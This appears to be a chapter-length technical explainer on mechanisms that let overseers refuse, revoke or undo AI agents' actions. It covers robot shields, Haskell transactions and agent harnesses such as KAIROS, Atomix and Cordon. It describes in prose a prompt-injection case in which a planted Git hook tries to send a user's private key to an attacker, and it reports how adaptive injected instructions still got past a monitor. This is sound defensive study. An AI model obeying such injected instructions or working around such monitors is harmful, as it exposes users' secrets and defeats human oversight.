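Some learned policies never write anything that resembles a plan. A walking robot's policy might output target positions for 12 joints, 50 times a second. Each output is an effect description, since no motor has acted on it yet, and software between the policy and the motors can log or replace it. But one set of 12 joint positions doesn't show where the robot is going, and no person can review 3,000 sets a minute.

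Engineers use automatic checks that don't require a plan. In *shielding*, a component between the policy and the motors checks each command against a formal safety rule, using a model of how the surroundings respond. It either offers the policy only safe commands or replaces unsafe ones after the policy chooses them. In *runtime assurance*, a closely related design from control engineering, a monitor hands control to a simpler, trusted backup controller before the system reaches a state that the backup couldn't recover from.

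For a wheeled robot, the backup can be the brake. Suppose that the robot drives toward a wall at speed *v*, that the shield checks a command every *T* seconds, and that the brakes slow the robot by *b* metres per second every second. The shield lets the robot keep its speed for one more period only if it could still stop afterwards:

```
distance to wall  ≥  v·T + v²/(2b)
```

At 2 metres per second, with checks every 0.02 seconds and *b* equal to 4, the right-hand side is 0.04 + 0.50 = 0.54 metres. The command passes at 0.60 metres and again at 0.56. At 0.52 it fails, so the shield brakes, and the robot stops 2 centimetres from the wall. The argument holds however the policy chose its commands, so it applies to any network. It does depend on the measured distance and on the brakes, which may work less well on a wet floor.

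Braking is not always a safe backup, because a running four-legged robot that freezes its joints may fall. *Agile But Safe* (2024) gives such a robot two learned policies, one for running toward a goal and one for recovering. When a third network estimates that the running policy is about to cause a collision, the recovery policy takes over. The system was trained in simulation and then ran a physical robot among obstacles at up to 3.1 metres per second. Because the network that triggers the recovery is also learned, the design lacks the guarantee that the braking formula gives.

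Shields work best for rules about physical quantities over the next few moments. A shield that checks only distances and speeds would let a delivery robot carry a parcel to the wrong house, because every movement on the way there is safe.

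## Refusing an action, withdrawing authority and undoing an effect

The fifth premise is that a refused or withdrawn action leaves no effects. Whether this is true depends on what "revoke" means. A company that regrets an invoice payment may want to stop the order before it reaches the bank, prevent the agent from making more payments, or get its money back.

| Meaning of "revoke" | Invoice example | What it requires |
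|---|---|---|
| Refuse a proposal | A reviewer rejects the payment before it runs | A component that waits for a verdict |
| Withdraw authority | The company cancels the agent's access to its bank account | A check on every use of that access |
| Undo an effect | The company recovers its 480 euros | A saved earlier state, or the recipient's cooperation |

Separating description from execution provides only refusal. The interpreter `askFirst` can stop before a payment, but once `perform` has sent the money, nothing in the free monad can reverse the payment. Refusing an action halfway through a plan can also leave the plan partly done. Suppose a plan pays an invoice and then records the payment in the company's accounts. If the reviewer allows the payment but refuses the recording, `askFirst` returns `Nothing` even though the money has already been sent.

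### Undo guaranteed by types

Haskell does have a type whose effects the runtime can always undo. Harris, Marlow and colleagues (2005), in *Composable Memory Transactions*, designed it for programs in which several threads run at once and share data. Its main operations are:

```haskell
readTVar  :: TVar a -> STM a
writeTVar :: TVar a -> a -> STM ()
retry     :: STM a
atomic    :: STM a -> IO a
```

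A `TVar` is a variable that threads can share, and a value of type `STM a` is a transaction on such variables. The function `atomic` turns a transaction into an `IO` action. While the transaction runs, it only records the values it reads and its pending changes in a private log. At the end, the runtime checks whether the values in the log that the transaction read are still current. If they are, the runtime makes all the changes at once. If another thread has changed one of those values, the runtime discards the log and reruns the transaction.

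This transaction reserves part of a budget:

```haskell
reserve :: TVar Int -> Int -> STM ()
reserve budget n =
  readTVar budget >>= \left ->
    if left < n then retry
                else writeTVar budget (left - n)
```

Suppose the budget is 1,000 euros, and one thread tries to reserve 480 while another reserves 700. The first thread reads 1,000 and records the new value, 520, in its log, where no other thread can read it. Before the first thread finishes, the second commits and the budget drops to 300. The runtime finds that the first thread's 1,000 is out of date, so it discards the log and restarts the transaction. This time the thread reads 300, which isn't enough, so it calls `retry`, which abandons the transaction and waits until another thread changes the budget.

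If the first thread had also sent 480 euros to the supplier during its failed attempt, discarding the log would not have brought the money back. Harris and colleagues give the example of a transaction that launches missiles if one number is larger than another. If the runtime reruns the transaction, it might launch a second salvo. The first launch could also be a mistake, if another thread changed both numbers after the transaction had read only one of them.

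Haskell's compiler rejects any transaction that contains `launchMissiles`, because `launchMissiles` has the type `IO ()` and no function turns an `IO` action into an `STM` transaction. The guarantee is strong because `STM` transactions can change only memory, which the runtime controls completely, but that restriction also excludes almost everything that people would want an agent to undo.

A contributor to a Haskell mailing-list thread, *SimonPJ and Tim Harris explain STM*, suspected that this answer would not satisfy practitioners, some of whom need to tie output to a transaction. One way to do so is for the transaction to return a description of the output:

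```haskell
payFrom :: TVar Int -> IO ()
payFrom budget =
  atomic (reserve budget 480 >>= \_ ->
            return (pay "NL-17" 480))
  >>= execute
```

Here `pay` is the free-monad version, which only builds a plan, and `execute` runs that plan after the transaction has committed. If the runtime repeats the transaction, it discards the unused plan and no money moves. But the reservation and the payment are now separate steps, so if the bank rejects the payment, the budget stays 480 euros lower until a second transaction restores it.

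### Withdrawing a permission

An overseer may also want to withdraw a permission that an agent already has. In an early Haskell mailing-list thread, *monads, modules, sandboxes*, programmers compared monads with capabilities, the unforgeable references to resources that TACIT also uses. Alastair Reid pointed out that operating systems can often revoke a capability at any time. For example, the kernel can change the permissions on a page of memory without waiting for the process that uses it. Capabilities that exist only in a type system often can't be revoked while a program is running, because the type checker finishes before the program starts.

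Reid also mentioned an exception on each side. David Walker had designed a type system that supports revocation, and on most Unix systems a process that has already opened a file keeps its access after someone changes the file's permissions.

A policy might let a program read files or use the network, but not both, so that it can't leak what it reads. Operating systems struggle to enforce this once processes pass capabilities to one another, and Reid suspected that type systems could do it better.

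The two approaches can work together. The check `pathOK` in the restricted type `RIO` runs at each file access, so it can look up a permission that an administrator has just changed.

Withdrawing a permission affects only later uses. Cancelling the PocketOS agent's token after the deletion would have protected other volumes but not restored the lost one. An operation that passed its permission check just before the withdrawal may still finish.

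### One payment through staging, delay and compensation

Three techniques make an agent's actions easier to take back. *Staging* applies a change to a private copy that can later be committed or discarded. (Programmers also use "staging" to mean a test copy of a whole system, as at PocketOS.) *Delay* holds a request in a queue before sending it. *Compensation* is a second action meant to repair the result of an action that cannot be erased.

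Suppose the agent handles the March invoice by marking it as paid in the accounts, ordering a payment of 480 euros to NL-17 and e-mailing the supplier. The harness stages the change to the accounts and holds the payment and the e-mail until 17:00. The bookkeeper then discovers that the invoice is forged.

| | Discovery at 16:00 | Discovery at 18:00 |
|---|---|---|
| Accounts | Discard the private copy | Add a correcting entry |
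| Payment | Delete the order from the queue | Ask for the money back, perhaps in vain |
| E-mail | Delete the draft | Send a correction to someone who has read the first message |

At 16:00 the company can cancel everything without any outsider noticing. Deleting an order from the queue is still a refusal, because the bank has not received it yet. The queue just gives the company more time to refuse. After 17:00 the company depends on compensation, and a forger has no reason to return the money.

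### Waiting for more evidence

KAIROS, the sandbox monitor by Hempel and colleagues, uses staging and delay to postpone difficult decisions. In their main example, an agent sets up a code repository by following a guide from the web. The guide recommends installing a hook, a script that Git runs at every commit. An attacker wrote this hook, but many legitimate projects use hooks, so refusing all of them would disrupt ordinary work.

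A monitor that can only allow or deny has to decide when the agent writes the hook, before there is any evidence of what the hook does. KAIROS can also defer the decision, keeping the hook in a private copy of the files while the agent continues. When the agent makes a commit, the hook runs and tries to send the user's private key to the attacker. KAIROS blocks that request and, based on this evidence, discards the hook too.

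KAIROS refuses an effect that an explicit rule forbids. It releases an effect if the values that control it, such as a recipient or a command, come from a trusted source and its data is allowed to go to its destination. It defers everything else to what Hempel and colleagues call a decision oracle. The oracle is a separate language model by default, but a person can take its place, and neither can override a refusal.

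How KAIROS holds a deferred effect depends on what the agent needs in order to continue:

| Deferred effect | What KAIROS does | What the agent receives |
|---|---|---|
| Writing or deleting a file | Applies the change to a private copy | A view of the files with its change |
| A request that changes something elsewhere | Holds the request at the network proxy | A stand-in reply |
| A request whose answer the agent needs | Has the oracle decide before sending it | The real answer or a refusal |

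Later steps may depend on a staged file or a stand-in reply, so KAIROS groups those steps with the deferred effect and commits or discards them together. The prototype can keep only one such group open, so if the agent attempts another effect that needs to be deferred, the oracle must first decide whether to commit or discard the open group.

In the invoice task, the account number comes from an untrusted file, so KAIROS would hold the payment and give the agent a stand-in reply. If the agent then tried to e-mail the supplier, the oracle would have to decide on the payment. It would be given the user's task and a note that the account number came from the invoice, not the user's message. Waiting helps less here than with the hook, because running a malicious hook in the sandbox exposes it, while a held payment looks the same whether the account belongs to the supplier or a forger.

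From outside, a discarded effect looks as if the agent had never proposed it, but the agent's conversation may still contain a stand-in reply to a request that was never sent. KAIROS treats the agent as a closed box and can't edit that conversation, so it notifies the agent of the refusal and tells it to continue with the rest of the task.

On AgentDojo with GPT-4.1, KAIROS reduced the share of successful attacks from 47.0% to 2.7%. Without attacks, the agent completed 85.1% of its tasks, slightly more than with no defence. In these runs, the fixed policy released 83% of effects by itself, and the oracle wrongly refused only one of the others. The oracle's calls increased token use by 17.7%.

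The strict version of this monitor stopped about as many attacks but halved task completion. Because it removed both the deferral and the oracle, the comparison doesn't show how much of the benefit comes from waiting and how much from having a second model judge the effect, which that model could also do immediately.

Deferral reduced utility more on AgentDyn's open-ended tasks. KAIROS cut attack success from 37.8% to 1.7%, and without attacks the agent completed 51.7% of its tasks, close to the undefended 53.3%. During attacks, however, KAIROS lowered task completion from 55.5% to 37.1%. Tasks retained 90% of their utility when they continued past one held effect, but only 62% after two or more. Hempel and colleagues attribute the loss to later steps that depended on held effects.

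An attacker who adapted the injected text over six rounds succeeded in 8.8% of cases, compared with 52.4% without a defence. The attacks that still worked targeted tasks in which the user had told the agent to follow a document, so the oracle treated the attacker's instructions in that document as the user's own.

### Holding messages and inspecting whole tasks

KAIROS cannot repair an effect after releasing it. *Atomix* (Mohammadi, Potamitis and colleagues, 2026) uses either holding or compensation, depending on the kind of effect. In its example, an agent books a flight, a hotel and a car, then sends a confirmation e-mail. Atomix makes the reservations immediately, because the agent needs the real confirmations and the reservations can be cancelled later. It holds the e-mail and tells the agent that it is queued. If the flight booking fails, Atomix cancels the other reservations and deletes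 the e-mail. If everything succeeds, it accepts the reservations as final and sends the e-mail.

Atomix also handles agents that try several plans at once, which resembles trying alternative transactions in Haskell. The harness chooses one plan, and Atomix discards or compensates for the effects of the others. But if a plan that wasn't chosen reserved a hotel room, the hotel has already received the reservation and may charge a fee to cancel it.

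Mohammadi and colleagues tested how Atomix holds back messages in 500 trials where a workflow failed or lost its authorization and should not have sent its message. Atomix sent none of them, and in 500 other trials it sent every valid message. A system that relied on compensation sent 400 of the 500 invalid messages, since a cancellation can't unsend an e-mail. Two other designs also sent no invalid messages, but needed more code for each tool.

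The result depends on developers labelling each tool correctly. When Mohammadi and colleagues deliberately mislabelled the e-mail tool, Atomix sent 300 of the 500 invalid messages.

They also made 30% of tool calls fail on 30 retail tasks from τ-bench. The agent finished 57% of the tasks without leaving duplicate or leftover effects. Replaying the workflow from a saved checkpoint did about as well, at 53%, and the other alternatives reached at most 7%. But replay was much worse at holding messages and sent 200 of the 500 invalid ones.

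Even with correct labels, a transaction that sends two e-mails can partly fail. Atomix has to send one before the other, so if the second fails permanently, the first has already been sent. No software above the mail servers can make the pair succeed or fail together, so Atomix records what it sent and reports the partial result to an operator.

*Cordon* (Chen, Dong and colleagues, 2026) uses the waiting time to inspect a task as a whole. For example, an agent investigating an outage might read a log that contains a secret key, summarize the log, write a note and prepare a message for the team's chat channel. Each call is reasonable by itself, but the summary may carry the key into the message. Cordon applies file changes to a private copy and holds outgoing messages in a queue called an *outbox*. It also records which earlier results each result came from. Before releasing anything, it can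 trace the message back through the summary to the log, and block the message if the channel isn't authorized to receive secrets.

Cordon stopped the harmful effect in all 45 risky workflows that Chen and colleagues constructed. Checks modelled on existing defences stopped 14, detected five only afterwards and missed 26. The comparison favours Cordon because the workflows involved five kinds of risk that become clear only across whole transactions, which Cordon is designed to inspect.

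### Restoring state and repairing effects

Version control doesn't always undo local changes completely. Chen and colleagues also had an agent make five kinds of mistake with files and checked whether it could resume its work after a rollback. Cordon passed all 15 trials, with a median rollback time of 4.17 milliseconds. Git's ordinary reset failed every trial, leaving a median of 73 differences, because it doesn't remove files that Git isn't tracking. With an added command to delete those files, Git passed 12 of 15 trials. The other three failures involved file permissions that Git had not saved.

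A running cloud service is harder to copy than a folder. Chen, Pan and colleagues (2025), in *STRATUS*, describe agents that repair such services by changing the real system and reversing the changes if they don't help. The system first records the current state and then runs up to 20 commands. It measures the severity of a failure as a weighted sum:

```
severity = w1 × alerts
         + w2 × broken service agreements
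         + w3 × unhealthy machines

keep the changes only if
  the system is still running and
  severity afterwards ≤ severity before
```

In one example, an agent shuts down a faulty service, installs a bad software image and restarts the service. Severity rises from 15 to 24 and then to 30, so an undo agent restores the recorded state and severity returns to 15.

Chen and colleagues prove that no other agent sees a state worse than the one the repair started from. The proof assumes that only one agent changes the system at a time and that the undo restores the earlier state exactly. STRATUS therefore rejects or replaces commands it cannot undo. For example, it moves a file to a backup volume instead of deleting it. Chen and colleagues concede that perfect undo is still impractical for some application data and for interactions with outside systems.

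The guarantee also covers only what other agents see. In another example, severity rises from 12 to 18 before falling to 9, and the service's customers may notice the increase. In tests on two sets of cloud failures, STRATUS repaired at least 1.5 times as many as the best earlier agents. Chen and colleagues credit this largely to its ability to try a repair, undo it and try another.

When nobody can restore the old state, compensation remains. Chang and Geng (2025), in *SagaLLM*, adapt the *saga*, a database technique from 1987 in which every step has a compensating step. Their example is a trip from San Francisco to Berlin and Cologne with five bookings. If the last one fails, the system works backwards through the other four:

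```
book:    flight to Berlin, Berlin hotel, train, Cologne hotel
fails:   return flight
cancel:  Cologne hotel, train, Berlin hotel, flight to Berlin
```

The order matters because later bookings depend on earlier ones. Chang and Geng describe the result as a return to the original state, but they define the compensation for a flight as cancelling it "with applicable fees". If the four cancellations cost a total of 150 euros, the traveller ends up with no bookings and 150 euros less than before. Anyone who looked for a hotel room in the meantime found one fewer available.

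The SagaLLM experiments, from March 2025, tested planning more than compensation. They used four scheduling problems, including a family dinner and a wedding, and involved no real bookings. In one, the model DeepSeek R1 responded to a 1:00 p.m. traffic alert by sending a driver to the airport, which he had already reached at 12:40. SagaLLM addresses this mistake by keeping a log of completed actions outside the model. Chang and Geng compare individual schedules and don't report success rates.

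| System | Holds before release | Rolls back | Compensates |
|---|---|---|---|
| KAIROS | File changes and some network requests | Staged files | Nothing |
| Atomix | E-mails, transfers and changes it can buffer | Buffered changes | Reservations, database writes and similar effects |
| Cordon | Outgoing messages and requests | Local file changes | Some released effects, using its records |
| STRATUS | Nothing | Changes to a cloud system | Nothing beyond its undo commands |
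| SagaLLM | Nothing | The planner's saved state | Bookings, with fees |

All of these systems need complete mediation to work as described. Atomix, for example, can't hold an e-mail if the agent sends it through a tool that has no adapter.

### A review queue for everyday services

Michael Chen, writing as miclchen in *What If AI Agents Had an Undo Button on Every API?*, proposes applying these ideas to ordinary office software. A layer between the agent and services such as Gmail and Slack would sort actions into three tiers:

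| Tier | Examples | Treatment |
|---|---|---|
| Auto-commit | Reading an e-mail, creating a file in a sandbox | Runs immediately |
| Buffer and review | Sending a routine e-mail, creating a calendar event | Becomes a draft or tentative event until someone approves it |
| Escalate | Making a purchase, writing to someone outside the company | Waits for explicit approval |

The design is a free-monad interpreter for office work, and Michael Chen draws that comparison explicitly.

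In the proposal's example, an agent spends an hour on recruiting. It drafts eight replies to candidates, proposes three interviews, updates five records and writes one summary for a manager. A reviewer would need an estimated three to five minutes to skim these 17 pending actions. Nobody has tested this estimate or measured how many mistakes such a reviewer would catch. The experiments with permission prompts give little reason to expect that someone skimming would notice a wrong account number.

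The invoice payment would go into the third tier and wait for approval. If the agent continued while waiting, it might tell the supplier that the money was on its way. Chen suggests either telling the agent that an action is pending or letting it work in a virtual world where the action has succeeded. The second option resembles the stand-in replies of KAIROS. Its results on AgentDyn suggest that this approach works less well when an agent has to continue past several held actions.

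The proposal also distinguishes actions by how long people have to undo them and who sees them before they are undone. Gmail lets a user recall a message for 30 seconds, and a deleted calendar event stays in the trash for 30 days. Anyone who read a chat message before it was deleted still knows what it said. Similarly, if the agent has read a password, refusing its next action doesn't remove the password from its conversation.

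### Approvals that go stale

While an action is held, the facts it was based on can change. Suppose the agent looks up the March invoice at 10:00, finds it unpaid and proposes to pay 480 euros to NL-17. The bookkeeper approves the payment at 10:05, and the harness holds it until 17:00. At noon a colleague who doesn't know about the held payment pays the same invoice by hand. At 17:00 the harness sends exactly the payment the bookkeeper approved, and the company pays twice.

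Memory transactions avoid this problem by checking, before they commit, that everything they read is still current. Atomix applies the same idea to tools. It records what an agent has read as well as what it intends to change, and aborts a waiting transaction if an earlier one has changed something it relied on. Locking a record only during each call isn't enough, because the record is unlocked while the model plans its next step.

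Mohammadi and colleagues tested this with several agents working on the same retail orders. One agent might cancel an order while another was changing its address. With four agents and a real model planning between reading and writing, locks on individual calls allowed three conflicting changes per run. With eight agents, they allowed seven. Atomix allowed none in either case. However, it tracks only changes made through its own adapters, so it would miss the colleague's payment unless it reread the invoice's status.

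The facts about the invoice are not all that can change. In Cordon's model, a transaction must satisfy the user's intent, the agent's authority and the company's policy as they stand when it commits. An approval covers one action on one object, with one destination and a limited time. For the payment, a final check along these lines might be:

```
send the payment only if
  the invoice is still unpaid, and
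  NL-17 is still the supplier's account, and
  the approval names NL-17 and 480 euros and has not expired, and
  the agent still has permission to pay
```

The last condition makes the withdrawal of authority apply to actions already in the queue. Without it, a company could cancel an agent's permission at 12:00, and a payment the agent had queued could still go out at 17:00.

Even this check leaves a short gap between confirming that the invoice is unpaid and sending the money. To close it, the payment system has to check and pay in one step, for example by accepting only one payment per invoice number. The harness can't guarantee this from outside if the colleague uses the bank directly.

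When a memory transaction fails its check, the runtime runs it again, because the same code will apply the programmer's rule to the new values. But an agent that starts again may write a different plan. The bookkeeper's approval of the old plan does not cover the new one, so the harness has to request approval again. A longer delay gives the company more time to discover a forged invoice, but it also makes these repeated requests more likely.
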